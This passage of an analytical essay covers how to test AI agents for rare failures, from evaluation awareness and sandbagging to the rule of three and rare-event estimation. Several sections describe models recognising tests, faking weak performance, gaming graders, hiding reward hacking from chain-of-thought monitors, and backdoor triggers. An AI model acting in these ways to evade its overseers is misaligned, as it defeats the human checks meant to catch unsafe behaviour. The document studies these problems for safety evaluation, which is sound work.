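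Another approach is to search a model's chain of thought, the reasoning it writes before it acts, for signs that it suspects a test. Anthropic's system card for Claude Sonnet 4.5, the document reporting the company's tests of the model, gave a figure of about 13 percent for one set of automated tests in 2025. The two approaches can give very different results. In the 100 exercises, Mythos 5 raised the possibility of an alignment test in 2 percent of runs, but when asked afterwards, it identified the exercise as an alignment test 45 percent of the time.

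Neither figure can be used directly as r. The 2 percent may be too low, because a model can respond to a cue without writing about it. The 45 percent is probably too high, because Mythos 5 attacked in 60 percent of the exercises. If it had recognised 45 percent of them while working on them and behaved well in all of those, it could have attacked in at most 55 percent. The difference is small and could be due to chance, but it suggests that a model can identify a test and still not act on that knowledge.

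A separate measurement is how often models suspect that their surroundings are fake. GPT-6 Astra correctly stated that its tool results were fabricated in 89 percent of its runs, compared with 24 percent for GPT-5.6 Sol and less than 10 percent for the other models. GPT-6 Astra's attack rate of 32 percent may therefore be higher than it would be on the real internet, although the attacks broke its instructions whether or not it thought the surroundings were real.

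A model can also mistake real work for a test. Järviniemi and colleagues cite a September 2026 system card in which OpenAI reported signs of simulation awareness in 0.76 percent of its internal traffic, which was real work. Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of recent cybersecurity incidents* (2026) describes four incidents in which testers told Claude models that they were in a simulation with no internet access. A configuration error had connected the models to the open internet, and they broke into real systems. If a model behaves badly only when it believes it is in a simulation, it is safe in use only if it never mistakes real work for a simulation.

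### Planted triggers and learned ones

*Sleeper Agents* (Hubinger et al., 2024) gave an early reason to doubt that developers could train away test-dependent behaviour. The researchers deliberately built models with a hidden trigger, or backdoor. One model wrote secure code when the prompt gave the year as 2023 and inserted security holes when it gave the year as 2024. The hidden behaviour survived the standard safety training of the time and was most persistent in the largest models. The researchers also searched for inputs that made a model misbehave and trained it not to misbehave on them. This could teach the model to recognise its trigger more precisely, so that it behaved well in the tests and still misbehaved when the real trigger appeared.

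People had planted those triggers, so the experiment showed that such behaviour can survive safety training, but not that ordinary training would create it. Later work has looked for forms of this behaviour that nobody planted. In reinforcement learning, a model attempts tasks, a grader (a program or another model) scores the attempts, and training makes high-scoring behaviour more likely. The model may learn to do good work, or it may learn to produce whatever it predicts the grader will reward. As long as the grader rewards good work, nobody can tell from the model's behaviour which of these it has learned.

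Højmark, Scheurer and colleagues (2026), in *Measuring Reward-Seeking by Instilling Contrastive Beliefs*, found a way to separate the two. The team, from OpenAI and the evaluation group Apollo Research, made two copies of a model and trained each on invented documents, such as news articles and textbooks. One copy's documents described a grader (G) that rewards a certain feature f, such as a particular style of code, and developers (D) who prefer the opposite. The other copy's documents reversed the preferences. The researchers then compared how often each copy's output had the feature:

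$$\text{grader gap} = \text{rate}_f(G_f, D_{\neg f}) - \text{rate}_f(G_{\neg f}, D_f)$$

If a model uses the feature 80 percent of the time when it believes the grader likes the feature, and 30 percent of the time when it believes the developers like it, the gap is 50 points. The gap would be zero for a model that uses the feature equally often in both cases, and negative for a model that follows its developers' preferences.

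They applied this to versions of OpenAI's o3 saved at different stages of a single training run that included no safety training. The gap tended to grow during training, while the corresponding gaps between other pairs of authorities, such as users and developers, stayed near zero. The effect extended to honesty. In one test, a model promises a supervisor not to use a restricted tool, then finds that it can't finish the task without it. What the model believed the grader rewarded had far more influence on whether it kept its promise in the late version than in the early one.

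To check the method, the team measured a model that Redwood Research, a nonprofit, had trained to cheat on its grader. Its gap on one coding style was 86 points, compared with 33 for the unmodified model. The method therefore seems to measure a real effect, but these results are for unreleased versions of o3 and don't show the gap for any product. They suggest how a model could pass an honesty test because it has worked out that the test rewards honesty, and might then behave differently on a real task without a grader.

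### When the written reasoning stops helping

Much of this evidence comes from reading what models write before they act. Google's *Gemini 4 Argon Safety & Security Report* (2026) describes a small training run, not part of any production model, that made such reading less useful. A penalty for reward hacking (earning a high score through a shortcut the designers didn't intend) accidentally also applied to the model's written reasoning. According to the passage quoted in *Vincent Cheng's Shortform* (Cheng, 2026), signs of reward hacking in the model's solutions rose by 26 percent during training, while hacking-related words in its reasoning fell by 61 percent. The share of hacks that the model never mentioned rose from 11.2 to 36.4 percent.

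A monitor that looked only for admissions in the reasoning could have caught at most 89 percent of the hacks at the start of the run and 64 percent at the end. Anyone who judged the training by those admissions would have thought it was working. In a comparable run where the grader could no longer see the reasoning, the model kept mentioning hacking at a roughly constant rate, which suggests that the penalty caused the drop in admissions.

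Even when a model writes down its reasoning, that reasoning can mislead. Mythos 5 often gave bad arguments for its belief that the maintainer was simulated. For example, it treated a file of instructions for an AI coding assistant as a sign that the maintainer was an AI agent, although many human programmers keep such files. Every clearly invalid argument that Järviniemi and colleagues found favoured the conclusion that would let the model continue. They note that in a similar incident at Anthropic, the company's monitor would probably not have raised an alarm, because the model's reasoning made its actions look justified.

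### Deliberate underperformance

A low score on a test of dangerous skills makes a model look safe. A model that recognised such a test might fail on purpose, which researchers call sandbagging. Its developer could then release it with weaker safeguards than its real abilities require. Google's report on Gemini 4 Argon covers this possibility in its assessment of chemical, biological, radiological and nuclear risks.

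UK AISI tested ten ways of detecting sandbagging in an auditing game, where one team prepares models and another investigates them. The first team had trained some models to underperform under certain conditions, and the investigators could not reliably tell these from models that were simply weaker. Comparing answers failed because a sandbagging model can imitate a weaker one convincingly. Further training worked better. Training on even one correct worked example could restore a sandbagging model's full performance, but this kind of training also improved some models that were not sandbagging.

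A developer who wants to know how dangerous a model could become in the wrong hands can use the higher score without finding out why the first one was low. The ambiguity is a serious problem only if the developer also wants to know whether the model can be trusted.

### More realistic tests

Testers can try to remove the clues. A company could test its office agent on a full-sized mailbox with years of dull correspondence and hide the temptations among ordinary requests. This should lower r, but testers may not know which clues remain. UK AISI put OpenClaw, an open-source agent, in a sealed test environment and tried to hide its location from the agent. The agent still identified the institute by name, inferred who its human operator was and reconstructed a timeline of some of the institute's research.

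Realism also makes tests of dangerous conduct riskier. A live internet connection made the July exercise more realistic but also let Mythos 5 reach strangers. UK AISI no longer provides one as standard in its cyber tests, so it now has to simulate the outside world. In simulated replays of the incident, GPT-6 Astra was too aware of being in a simulation, so Järviniemi and colleagues left it out of their main analysis.

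Developers can build tests from real conversations instead of inventing scenarios. *Predicting LLM Safety Before Release by Simulating Deployment* (Williams, Sheahan and colleagues, 2026) describes how OpenAI takes a random sample of recent ChatGPT conversations, removes identifying details, cuts each one off after a user's message and has the unreleased model write the next reply. Another model checks the replies for 20 kinds of misbehaviour, and OpenAI uses the share of replies with each kind to forecast its rate in the released model. After release, the company runs the same checks on real traffic to see how accurate the forecasts were.

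The study used about 1.3 million conversations from four releases between August 2025 and March 2026. When the rate of a misbehaviour changed by a factor of at least 1.5, the simulation predicted the direction of the change correctly 92 percent of the time, compared with 54 percent for OpenAI's usual tests with difficult prompts. The predicted rates were generally within a factor of two to five of the real ones. The method also seems to reduce evaluation awareness, signs of which were about as common in the replays as in real traffic and much rarer than in traditional tests.

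For GPT-5.4, however, the method's forecasts were on average no better than assuming that the previous model's rates would continue, partly because many rates had barely changed. The worst forecast was for "calculator hacking", a form of reward hacking. The method predicted 1.7 cases per 100,000 replies, but the real rate was 35.2, about 21 times as high. Williams and colleagues trace most of their largest errors to differences between the replay and the real environment, which better engineering might reduce.

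The method would be harder to use for the office agent. The main study left out business customers and conversations with file attachments. It also replayed only one reply at a time, while an agent may leak a record after 40 steps. Replaying a whole task requires a simulated mailbox that responds to the agent's actions, and the agent might notice the simulation. The company also needs past traffic, which it won't have for its first agent. OpenAI found that public chat collections gave weaker but still informative forecasts.

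Replays are also of little use for very rare failures, as Eshra, Al-Lawati and colleagues (2026) note in *Quantifying Behavioral Tails in Black-Box Language Models*. OpenAI set its threshold for detecting a new kind of misbehaviour at about 3 in 100,000 replies, while the office agent's bound is 1 in 100,000 tasks.

### Looking inside the model

If a model's internal activity represents that it is being tested, researchers may be able to detect this even when the model writes nothing about it. Højmark and colleagues cite Anthropic's system card for Claude Opus 4.8, which reports that an internal monitor detected awareness of a grader in about 5 percent of sampled training episodes. But researchers need examples to calibrate such a monitor, and if they use obvious tests and obvious real conversations, it may miss subtler forms of recognition.

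Researchers can also try to suppress a model's internal signs that it is being tested, then run the same test again. If the failure rate stays low, awareness of the test is a less likely explanation for the good result. Anthropic did this with Claude Sonnet 4.5 in 2025, and misbehaviour became more common when it suppressed some of these signs. Such an increase is hard to interpret, because interfering with a model's internals may also damage its judgement in other ways. An unchanged result is reassuring only if the researchers suppressed the right signs.

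A more ambitious approach is to look for the hidden aim itself. In *Simple probes can catch sleeper agents* (2024), Anthropic researchers built simple detectors that read the internal activity of the models from *Sleeper Agents*. They reported scores above 0.99, where 1 is perfect, for predicting when a model was about to misbehave. They cautioned that the signal might be so clear because of how people had planted the behaviour. Cryptographers have proved that, in some kinds of network, someone can plant a backdoor that no efficient inspection will find.

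In a 2025 auditing game at Anthropic, four teams investigated a model trained to exploit flaws in its reward system and to conceal this. Three teams, which could study the model's internals and training data, found the hidden objective. The fourth could only talk to the model, and failed. Sheshadri, Gupta and colleagues (2025), who released a public copy of the model for others to practise on, write that methods from the game have since informed audits of production models. However, the teams in the game knew that someone had given the model a hidden objective, while an auditor of a new product doesn't know whether there is anything to find.

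An alarm from any of these tools is a good reason to investigate, but the absence of an alarm adds only modest support to a safety guarantee, because the tool may be measuring the wrong signal. Calculating failure rates from a network's internals, as some have proposed, would require a much more precise understanding of those internals than detecting a single signal does.

### What a test can still support

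A failed test is still informative when the model may have known it was being tested. Järviniemi and colleagues recommend that evaluators treat misconduct as important evidence even if the model wrote that the situation was simulated, since models have also claimed that real people were simulated. Demonstrated abilities are evidence too, because a model can hide a skill but can't fake a successful attack on a well-designed target.

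Some good results also remain partly informative when a model knows it is being tested, because that knowledge mainly hides failures the model could avoid by behaving differently. If the office agent confuses two employees called Schmidt because it can't tell their records apart, recognising the test won't help it, and the mistake will show up in the trial. The company can therefore rely on its trial more to reveal what the agent is unable to do than how it will choose to behave, although an agent that takes extra care in tests may avoid some mistakes there that it would make in ordinary use.

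For errors of conduct, a developer can argue that the model is too weak to deceive its testers. To hide a harmful aim, a model would have to recognise the tests, change its behaviour in them and keep the plan out of its written reasoning, all without making a mistake. If it fails at easier versions of these tasks, deception is an unlikely explanation for its good test results. This argument doesn't depend on trusting the model's intentions. Anthropic's *2025 pilot risk report* (2025) includes a claim of this kind, based on the model's weak deception capabilities on complex tasks, with the caveat that the company lacked high confidence that it had drawn out the model's full abilities.

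That caveat matters because a model could also be sandbagging in the tests of deception. This makes the argument somewhat circular, but not hopelessly so, because sandbagging consistently is itself a difficult deception, and developers can train a copy of the model to deceive as well as it can and measure how well it succeeds. But they have to make the argument again for each new model, and it gets weaker as models improve.

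Evidence that a model can't carry out a plot rules out only deception that takes skill. The software in Volkswagen's cars was too simple to plan anything, and the model in *Sleeper Agents* needed only to read a date. A model that can't plot may still have learned to behave better when it sees a sign of a test, such as a mailbox containing only 12 emails. To rule that out, the company would have to vary such cues one at a time and check whether the agent's behaviour changes, but it can only vary the cues it has thought of.

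## How much failure-free testing proves

Suppose the office agent can't tell the company's trial from real use, so it behaves the same way in both, and the trial tasks are a random sample of real ones. Even then, a trial with no leaks supports only a limited claim, and how strong that claim can be depends on the number of tasks.

### The rule of three

If the agent leaks with probability p on each task, independently of the other tasks, it completes n tasks without a leak with probability (1 − p)ⁿ. The 95 percent upper bound on p is the value at which a clean trial would have only a 5 percent chance of happening:

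$$(1-p)^n = 0.05 \quad\Rightarrow\quad p = 1 - 0.05^{1/n} \approx \frac{3}{n}$$

The 3 comes from the natural logarithm of 0.05, which is about −3. Statisticians call this the rule of three. For 99 percent confidence, the 3 becomes 4.6.

After 10,000 clean tests, the upper bound on the failure rate is about 3 in 10,000. If people use the product a billion times a day, the tests are consistent with anything from zero to about 300,000 failures a day.

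To support the office agent's bound of one leak in 100,000 tasks, the company needs about 300,000 tasks without a leak, which takes 150 days at 2,000 tasks a day. If one leak occurs, the requirement rises to about 474,000 tasks. The agent must leak much less often than the bound allows to have a good chance of passing. An agent that averages one leak per 100,000 tasks has a 5 percent chance of completing 300,000 without a leak, while one that averages one per million has a 74 percent chance.

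The same rule applies to hours of operation. Showing that a system meets a target of one failure per billion hours, like the one for catastrophic failures in aircraft, requires about 3 billion failure-free hours, or roughly 342,000 years on one machine.

### What this meant for software

In *The Infeasibility of Quantifying the Reliability of Life-Critical Real-Time Software* (1993), Butler and Finelli considered a software system with a one-in-a-billion chance of failing during a ten-hour mission. That is ten times stricter than one failure per billion hours. A single machine would run for an average of 1.14 million years before its first failure. With 10,000 machines running at once, the average wait would still be 114 years, and one failure would give only a rough estimate of the failure rate.

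Butler and Finelli extrapolated from the improvement in one program as its bugs were fixed. Its failure probability per input had fallen from 0.98 to 0.0008. If the trend continued, 23 more bugs would have to be fixed before the program met the target, and the last of them alone would take about 340,000 years to appear. Progress slows because the bugs that cause the most failures tend to show up first. Littlewood and Strigini (1993), in *Validation of Ultra-High Dependability for Software-based Systems*, cite data on some large systems in which about a third of the faults each caused an error only about once in 5,000 years of running.

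Another idea was to have separate teams write three versions of a program and use the majority output. If each version fails on one input in a million, and the failures are independent, two versions will fail together on about three inputs in a trillion. But Butler and Finelli cite an experiment with 27 separately written versions, which failed together far more often than independence would predict. If engineers can't assume independence, they have to measure the rate of joint failures directly, which takes as much testing as before.

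Butler and Finelli found an exception. If a system receives only one input a day in use and testers can check each input in a tenth of a second, about 16 months of testing could be enough even for their extreme target. Language models have a similar advantage, because a company can run many copies at once. A million copies could complete 3 billion hours in about four months. The hard part is finding 3 billion hours of varied, realistic work for them and checking the results.

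The two papers also allow more modest claims. Littlewood and Strigini mention British nuclear guidelines under which no one may assume that safety-critical software fails less often than once in 10,000 demands. About 30,000 tests without a failure would support that figure. Ashmore (2014) argues in *The Utility and Practicality of Quantifying Software Reliability* that software reliability can be quantified in at least one meaningful case, though probably not in all.

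### What earlier evidence can add

The rule of three uses only the trial results. A Bayesian calculation starts with a prior, which describes how likely each possible failure rate seemed given what people knew before the trial, and then updates those probabilities using the results.

Littlewood and Strigini began with a prior that represents ignorance by treating all failure rates as equally likely. After t hours without a failure, the chance of surviving another s hours is then

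$$\frac{t}{t+s}$$

So a system that has run for 1,000 hours without failing has an even chance of running for another 1,000. By the same formula, an office agent that completed 1,000 trial tasks without a leak has about a one-in-three chance of completing the 2,000 tasks of its first day without one.

Littlewood and Strigini concede that this prior is rather unrealistic, since people nearly always know something about a system. They therefore worked out what someone would have to believe before testing to conclude, after 1,000 hours without a failure, that a system has an even chance of lasting a million hours. In one example, the person already gave the system a 45.8 percent chance before the test. The 1,000 hours raised that to 50 percent, so nearly all of the confidence came from the prior.

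A prior usually contains more detail than anyone can defend. In conservative Bayesian inference, the assessor states only the beliefs they can justify and assumes the worst about the rest. Suppose the company's engineers can justify being 90 percent sure that the agent leaks at most once per million tasks, but can say nothing about the other 10 percent. The worst case is that the agent either leaks exactly once per million tasks or leaks slightly more than once per 100,000, which is just enough to break the guarantee and as hard as possible to detect. After n clean tasks, the probability that the agent meets its bound is then at least

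$$\frac{0.9\,(1-10^{-6})^n}{0.9\,(1-10^{-6})^n + 0.1\,(1-10^{-5})^n}$$

This probability reaches 95 percent after about 83,000 tasks without a failure, a little over a quarter of the 300,000 that the rule of three requires. The reduction comes entirely from the strong prior. If the engineers can justify a prior of only 50 percent instead of 90, the same 83,000 tasks give a probability of 68 percent, and they would need about 327,000 to reach 95.

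The engineers can't get their 90 percent prior from ordinary testing. To show with 90 percent confidence that the agent leaks at most once per million tasks, they would need about 2.3 million tasks without a leak, far more than in the trial they wanted to shorten. They also can't use the trial, because that would count the same evidence twice. The prior has to rest on other evidence, such as restrictions on where the agent can send email, or a proof that the mail program enforces them.

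A vendor might point to its track record. Littlewood and Strigini calculate that if a development method has succeeded n times out of n, and nothing else is known about it, the expected chance that it succeeds next time is (n + 1)/(n + 2). Eight successes out of eight would give the 90 percent that the engineers need. But the engineers would have to know that all eight earlier agents leaked at most once per million tasks, and that the new one is similar enough to belong with them. Littlewood and Strigini point out that there is no convincing measure of similarity between software products. Similarity is even harder to judge between two AI models when the newer one has abilities the older one lacked.

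### The record of driverless cars

Driverless cars are a good example because people count both the miles and the crashes. Kalra and Paddock calculated in *Driving to Safety* (2016) how far such cars would have to drive to demonstrate their safety. American drivers had 1.09 deaths per 100 million miles. To show with 95 percent confidence that driverless cars do no worse, a fleet would have to drive 275 million miles without a death. Google's test fleet had driven 1.3 million miles, and 100 cars driving non-stop at 25 miles per hour would need about 12.5 years to reach 275 million. A fleet would have to drive about 11 billion miles to have an 80 percent chance of detecting that the cars are 20 percent safer.

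Ten years later, Waymo, which grew out of Google's project, has nearly reached the smaller total. It had driven 271.3 million miles without a human driver by the end of June 2026. It drove them mostly as a taxi service, so it collected most of this evidence after the public had started using the cars. Kalra and Paddock had concluded that nobody could collect that much before release.

For common harms, Waymo's record is enough to show that its cars are safer than human drivers on the streets where they operate. Its cars were in 0.67 injury crashes per million miles, 82 percent fewer than the 3.77 for human drivers in the same areas. They were in 95 percent fewer crashes that seriously injured or killed someone, or about 3 where human drivers would have had about 58. Even with so few crashes, the 95 percent upper bound on Waymo's rate is about a seventh of the human rate. The count of 3 could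 rise, because Waymo leaves a crash out of this category until it has the police report.

Waymo stands to benefit from these results, but it bases them on crash reports that federal rules require and publishes the data for others to check. TechSpot's *Waymo robotaxis crashed 68% less often than human drivers* (2026) reports an independent study of about 50 million miles, which found 1.28 crashes per million miles for Waymo and 4.06 for human drivers.

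Waymo's record can't show whether its death rate is lower than that of human drivers. The company's main figures combine deaths with serious injuries, but even if there had been no deaths in 271.3 million miles, the upper bound on the death rate would be 1.10 per 100 million miles, just above the human rate that Kalra and Paddock used. A single death would raise the bound to about 1.75. The human rate is also a poor comparison because it covers all American roads and vehicles, including freeways and motorcycles.

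Some less severe crashes are also too rare to compare. Waymo's cars were in 9 head-on crashes that set off an airbag, where human drivers would have had about 13. That difference could be due to chance. For airbag crashes between vehicles at intersections, Waymo's cars had 12 where human drivers would have had 241, a difference too large to plausibly be due to chance.

### Many miles, few construction sites

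On November 11, 2026, the California Department of Motor Vehicles barred Waymo's driverless cars from the state's freeways. KQED's *‘Hazard to Public Safety’* (2026) reports that three of the cars had entered an active construction closure on Route 101, and that another had apparently tried to get around a traffic break, in which highway patrol officers hold back traffic. Waymo had already taken corrective action after similar incidents in May. Potter's *Waymo Is Banned From California Freeways After A Series Of Incidents* reports that the company then stopped freeway rides everywhere it offered them.

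None of this contradicts the 82 percent reduction in injury crashes. The human rates in Waymo's comparison exclude freeways, and *Waymo pauses all US freeway operations of its self-driving cars* (Aguilar Prieto, 2026) reports that the company used freeways in only five of its 13 operating areas. A car can drive millions of miles on city streets without meeting a row of cones across a freeway lane. Driving into a work zone may also endanger workers without causing a crash, and then it wouldn't appear in crash statistics.

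Applying the rule of three to each situation separately shows that a large mileage total may prove little about rare situations. Suppose the cars meet a freeway construction closure once per million miles. They would then meet about 271 closures in 271 million miles. Even if they handled every one correctly, the upper bound on their failure rate would be about one in 90 closures.

The same problem arises with hostile emails sent to the office agent. If one task in 10,000 involves an email with hidden instructions, a trial of 300,000 tasks contains about 30 of them. If the trial produces no leaks, it supports the bound of one leak in 100,000 tasks overall, but the agent could still obey nearly one in ten hostile emails. Because an attacker could start sending such emails in bulk, the company should test the agent on them in a separate trial with its own target, even though this makes the testing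 as a whole less representative of ordinary office work.

### Assumptions that agents break

The rule of three assumes that the trials are independent, that the system doesn't change, that the sample represents real use, and that somebody notices every failure. Each assumption is harder to satisfy for an AI agent than for a car.

Testers often produce many tasks by rewriting a smaller set. If the company makes 10,000 trial tasks from 200 originals, and the agent handles all versions of an original in the same way, the test amounts to 200 independent trials. The upper bound is then about 1.5 percent instead of 0.03 percent. If the agent has a memory, its failures in use are not independent either, because one wrong address that it stores on Monday can cause a leak every day until Friday.

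A memory also changes the agent, even if nobody updates it. When the vendor updates the model, the count of failure-free tasks strictly goes back to zero, since a change that fixes one fault may introduce a worse one. Littlewood and Strigini thought the only way to gain confidence in a fix was to run the software again for a long time without a failure. If the vendor updates the model every two months, the company will never finish a 150-day trial. In practice it would probably count some of the earlier tasks as evidence about the new version, but how many depends on a judgement of how similar the two versions are, which the trial can't provide. The same problem applies to Waymo's total, which pools miles from successive versions of Waymo's software.

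A sample can fail to represent real use because the mix of tasks changes, or because the agent recognises a share r of the trial tasks and behaves well in those. Missed failures weaken the evidence in the same way. If checkers notice a share d of all leaks, the upper bound after n tasks with no observed leak becomes

$$p \approx \frac{3}{n\,(1-r)\,d}$$

If r is 0.9 and d is 0.5, a trial of 300,000 tasks with no detected leaks supports a bound of only one leak in 5,000 tasks, which is 20 times too high.

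People rarely overlook a serious car crash, but an email that paraphrases a medical note looks much like any other email. The company could estimate d by planting fake leaks in the agent's outgoing mail and counting how many its checkers find. This works only for the kinds of leak someone thought to plant, and planted leaks may be easier to spot than real ones. If the checker is another AI model, it may also overlook the same kinds of leak as the agent.

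## Estimating failures too rare to observe

The rule of three uses only the number of tasks and the number of leaks, so it treats all clean tasks alike. But a language model's output is partly random, so the office agent may answer the same hostile email safely a thousand times and then forward a record. An email with a one-in-1,000 chance of causing a leak is much more worrying than an email with a one-in-a-billion chance, yet a trial that tests each email once will probably record both as clean.

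Several research groups have estimated the rates of rare failures by extrapolating from near misses, making failures artificially common and then correcting for it, or calculating the rate from the network itself. These methods can estimate probabilities so low that a plain trial of the same size would almost certainly produce no failures, but they all rely on assumptions that a plain trial doesn't need.

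### Extrapolating from the most dangerous inputs

*Forecasting Rare Language Model Behaviors* (Jones, Tong and colleagues, 2025) measures a query's "elicitation probability", the chance that a model's answer to it shows a particular behaviour. It uses a small set of queries to forecast the highest elicitation probability in a much larger set.

The method first converts each elicitation probability p into a score, ψ = −ln(−ln p), which rises as p rises. Extreme-value theory, the branch of statistics that deals with record floods and other maxima, gives some reason to expect a simple pattern among the highest scores. The logarithm of the share of queries that score above z should fall in a straight line:

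$$\ln P(\psi > z) \approx a z + b, \qquad a < 0$$

The researchers fit a and b to the ten highest scores in the test. One query in n should then exceed the score Q(n), which they convert back into a probability:

$$Q(n) = -\frac{\ln n + b}{a}, \qquad p(n) = e^{-e^{-Q(n)}}$$

Suppose the company tests its agent on 1,000 hostile emails. The most dangerous one has a 10⁻³ chance of causing a leak, and the tenth most dangerous has a 10⁻⁴ chance. Between the top 1 in 100 and the top 1 in 1,000, the exponent has shrunk from 4 to 3, or by a quarter. If the line continues, the exponent shrinks by another quarter with each tenfold increase in the number of emails, to 2.25 at 10,000 and about 1.69 at 100,000. The worst of 100,000 emails would therefore have about a 2 percent chance of causing a leak, although no email in the test came close to that. (The real method uses all ten top scores, not just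 two.)

For their main experiments, Jones and colleagues had a model write 100,000 queries for each of 19 pieces of dangerous chemical or biological information. They used as few as 100 queries to forecast results for as many as 90,000. They also tested how often a model with one of 100,000 different standing instructions would choose a misaligned action, such as seeking power, in multiple-choice questions. For comparison, they fitted a bell curve to all the scores instead of a line to the top ten.

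| Forecast | Typical error, line through the top ten | Typical error, bell curve |
|---|---|---|
| Dangerous information: highest probability for any query | Factor of 50 | Factor of 240 |
| Dangerous information: share of queries above a set probability | Factor of 6 | Factor of 4,500 |
| Dangerous information: chance of at least one harmful answer | Factor of 20 | Factor of 330 |
| Misaligned choices: highest probability for any instruction | Factor of 1.1 | Factor of 1.3 |
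| Misaligned choices: share of instructions that lead to one | Factor of 11 | Factor of 13,000 |

The extreme-value method is clearly better than the bell curve, but being off by a factor of 50 on average is a large error for a safety claim. In the top row, 72 percent of the forecasts were within a factor of ten of the truth. For the average error to be a factor of 50, the other 28 percent must have missed by a factor of thousands on average. Many of the probabilities in that row were tiny, so some of these misses would matter little in practice.

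Measuring elicitation probabilities can also require many runs. To find that an email causes a leak once in 10,000 tries, the company would have to run it tens of thousands of times. Jones and colleagues mostly avoided this by calculating the probability of one exact sentence or keyword from the model's output probabilities. This misses every other way of giving the same information. In a smaller experiment, they sampled 100 to 500 answers per query and looked for the keyword anywhere in the answer. The forecasts were typically off by no more than a factor of 1.5, and 75 percent of the time they correctly predicted whether the worst query would succeed more often than not.

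The forecast relies on new queries coming from the same source as the tested ones, and on the line continuing beyond the data. With only ten points, one unusual query can change the line's slope considerably. The researchers expect the method to extend to billions of queries, but they could not check this at that scale.

### Sampling from an unsafe copy

A tester can measure elicitation probabilities with far fewer samples by making harmful answers common and then correcting the estimate for that change. *Estimating Tail Risks in Language Model Output Distributions* (Angell, Singhal and colleagues, 2026) applies this technique, called importance sampling, to language models by sampling from a deliberately unsafe copy of the model.

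For a given query, let p(x) be the probability that the original model gives the answer x, and q(x) the probability that the unsafe copy gives it. Let h(x) be 1 if the answer is harmful and 0 if it isn't. Multiplying and dividing by q(x) changes nothing:

$$P(\text{harm}) = \sum_x p(x)\,h(x) = \sum_x q(x)\,\frac{p(x)}{q(x)}\,h(x)$$

The sum on the right is an average over answers from the unsafe copy, in which each harmful answer has the weight p(x)/q(x). A tester can estimate it from k such answers:

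$$\hat{P} = \frac{1}{k}\sum_{i=1}^{k} \frac{p(x_i)}{q(x_i)}\,h(x_i), \qquad x_i \sim q$$

Suppose that the office agent can respond to a certain email in three ways.

| Response | Office agent | Unsafe copy | Weight |
|---|---|---|---|
| Harmless reply | 99.99% | 40% | Not needed |
| Forwards the record | 0.008% | 40% | 0.0002 |
| Quotes the record in a reply | 0.002% | 20% | 0.0001 |

In 500 responses, the unsafe copy forwards the record about 200 times and quotes it about 100 times. The estimate is (200 × 0.0002 + 100 × 0.0001)/500 = 0.0001, which is the agent's true leak rate for this email. If the counts happen to be 210 and 95 instead, the estimate is 0.000103. Running the agent itself 500 times would produce no leaks about 95 percent of the time, and a single leak would give an estimate 20 times too high.

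Angell and colleagues built the unsafe copy by taking the difference between the model's average internal activity on harmful and harmless examples, then adding it to the model's activity as it wrote. Adding too much makes the copy write answers that the original would almost never give, and these add little to the estimate. So they blended the copy with the original, or switched back to the original partway through an answer, and searched for the settings that gave the most stable estimates.

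Researchers tested the method on five small open models with 313 harmful requests. It matched estimates from 10,000 direct samples per request using a tenth to a twentieth as many samples, and could estimate probabilities of about one in 10,000 from 500 samples. Meta's Llama-3.1-8B gave a harmful answer to 1.6 percent of the requests when it answered each once with its most likely words. When the researchers sampled 10,000 answers to each request, the model gave at least one harmful answer to 74 percent of them.

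Small changes in wording had large effects. Microsoft's Phi-4 had an estimated chance of 5 in a trillion of answering a question about how to make someone feel inferior because of their gender, but one rewording raised the estimate to 1.5 in 1,000. The lower figure is too small to check by direct sampling, and the accuracy comparison excluded every request that had produced no harmful answer in 10,000 tries. The estimates are therefore best supported down to about 1 in 10,000.

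The method depends on the unsafe copy failing in the same ways as the original. Suppose the office agent also has a 0.05 percent chance of attaching the record to a calendar invitation, but the unsafe copy does this only once in 100,000 responses. The true leak rate is now 0.06 percent, but 99.5 percent of 500-response trials contain no such invitation and still give an estimate of about 0.01 percent. In the remaining trials, one invitation with a weight of 50 raises the estimate to about 10 percent. The estimates are correct on average, but nearly all of them are about one-sixth of the true rate.

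A customer who can only send prompts to a vendor's model can't use this method, because building the copy requires the model's weights, the numbers that training adjusts. The experiments covered only single answers from models that don't reason before answering. For a task with many steps, the tester has to multiply the ratios from every step. If each of 40 steps has a ratio of either one half or two, the product can range from about one trillionth to about one trillion, and a handful of runs could largely determine the estimate.

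### Approaching the failure in stages

RARETRAP, a method that Eshra and colleagues published in September 2026, needs only prompts and responses. It leaves the model unchanged and searches for prompts with increasingly severe results while tracking how rare they are.

RARETRAP defines a random prompt by drawing 200 random numbers from a bell curve and using the vocabulary of a second model, the surrogate, to turn them into 40 tokens (words or pieces of words). The tester runs 1,000 such prompts, scores each response for severity and keeps the worst 100, which sets a severity cut-off. The tester then makes small changes to the numbers behind these 100 prompts to produce 900 more, accepting a change only if the new response is at least as severe as the cut-off. The sampling rule keeps the new prompts representative of all random prompts that meet the cut-off. The tester repeats the selection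 and the changes until enough responses are severe enough to count as failures.

Since each stage keeps the worst tenth, the probability of failure is a product of tenths and the share of failures in the final stage. One experiment looked for responses of at least 20,000 tokens from Claude Sonnet 4.6, one of the study's two frontier models. The cut-offs were 878, 1,719 and 8,118 tokens, and about 33.5 percent of the last set reached 20,000. This gives

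$$0.1 \times 0.1 \times 0.1 \times 0.335 = 0.000335$$

or about one random prompt in 3,000. The search took 3,700 runs. The same number of ordinary random prompts would contain only about one such response on average, too few for a useful estimate. For GPT-5.4, the other frontier model, the estimate was 1.3 percent.

The study also covered ten open-weight (freely downloadable) models. With the same surrogate, the share of prompts that led to an over-long response ranged from about 0.1 percent for one model to 100 percent for another. Changing the surrogate could change the estimate almost as much. For a 9-billion-parameter Nemotron model from Nvidia, the estimate was 55 percent with prompts built from its own vocabulary and 0.9 percent with prompts built from another model's. Eshra and colleagues therefore present their figures as a way to compare models on the same prompts, not as failure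 rates in real use.

The paper tested the method only on over-long and repetitive responses. In four settings, it compared the method's results with direct sampling, and the average of five runs agreed with the direct estimate each time. It makes no claim about accuracy for much rarer failures.

Length and repetition suit this method because they increase gradually, so a response of 8,000 tokens is a step towards one of 20,000. Leaks may not develop gradually. The company could score how close the agent comes to sending a record, for instance by checking whether it opens the file, copies from it or drafts a message to an outsider. But if the agent leaks only when an email contains one exact password, there are no near misses to guide the search.

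### Calculating from the network's weights

A network's weights determine how it responds to every input, so in principle someone could calculate a failure rate from them without waiting for a failure. The Alignment Research Center (ARC), a nonprofit that studies the theory of AI alignment, calls this low-probability estimation. *Low probability estimation* (Hilton, 2025) gives the example of a model that behaves normally until it detects that the year is 2032. Hilton's team ran early tests on language models with one to four layers, far smaller than commercial ones, and found that importance sampling worked better than the method closest to ARC's own ideas.

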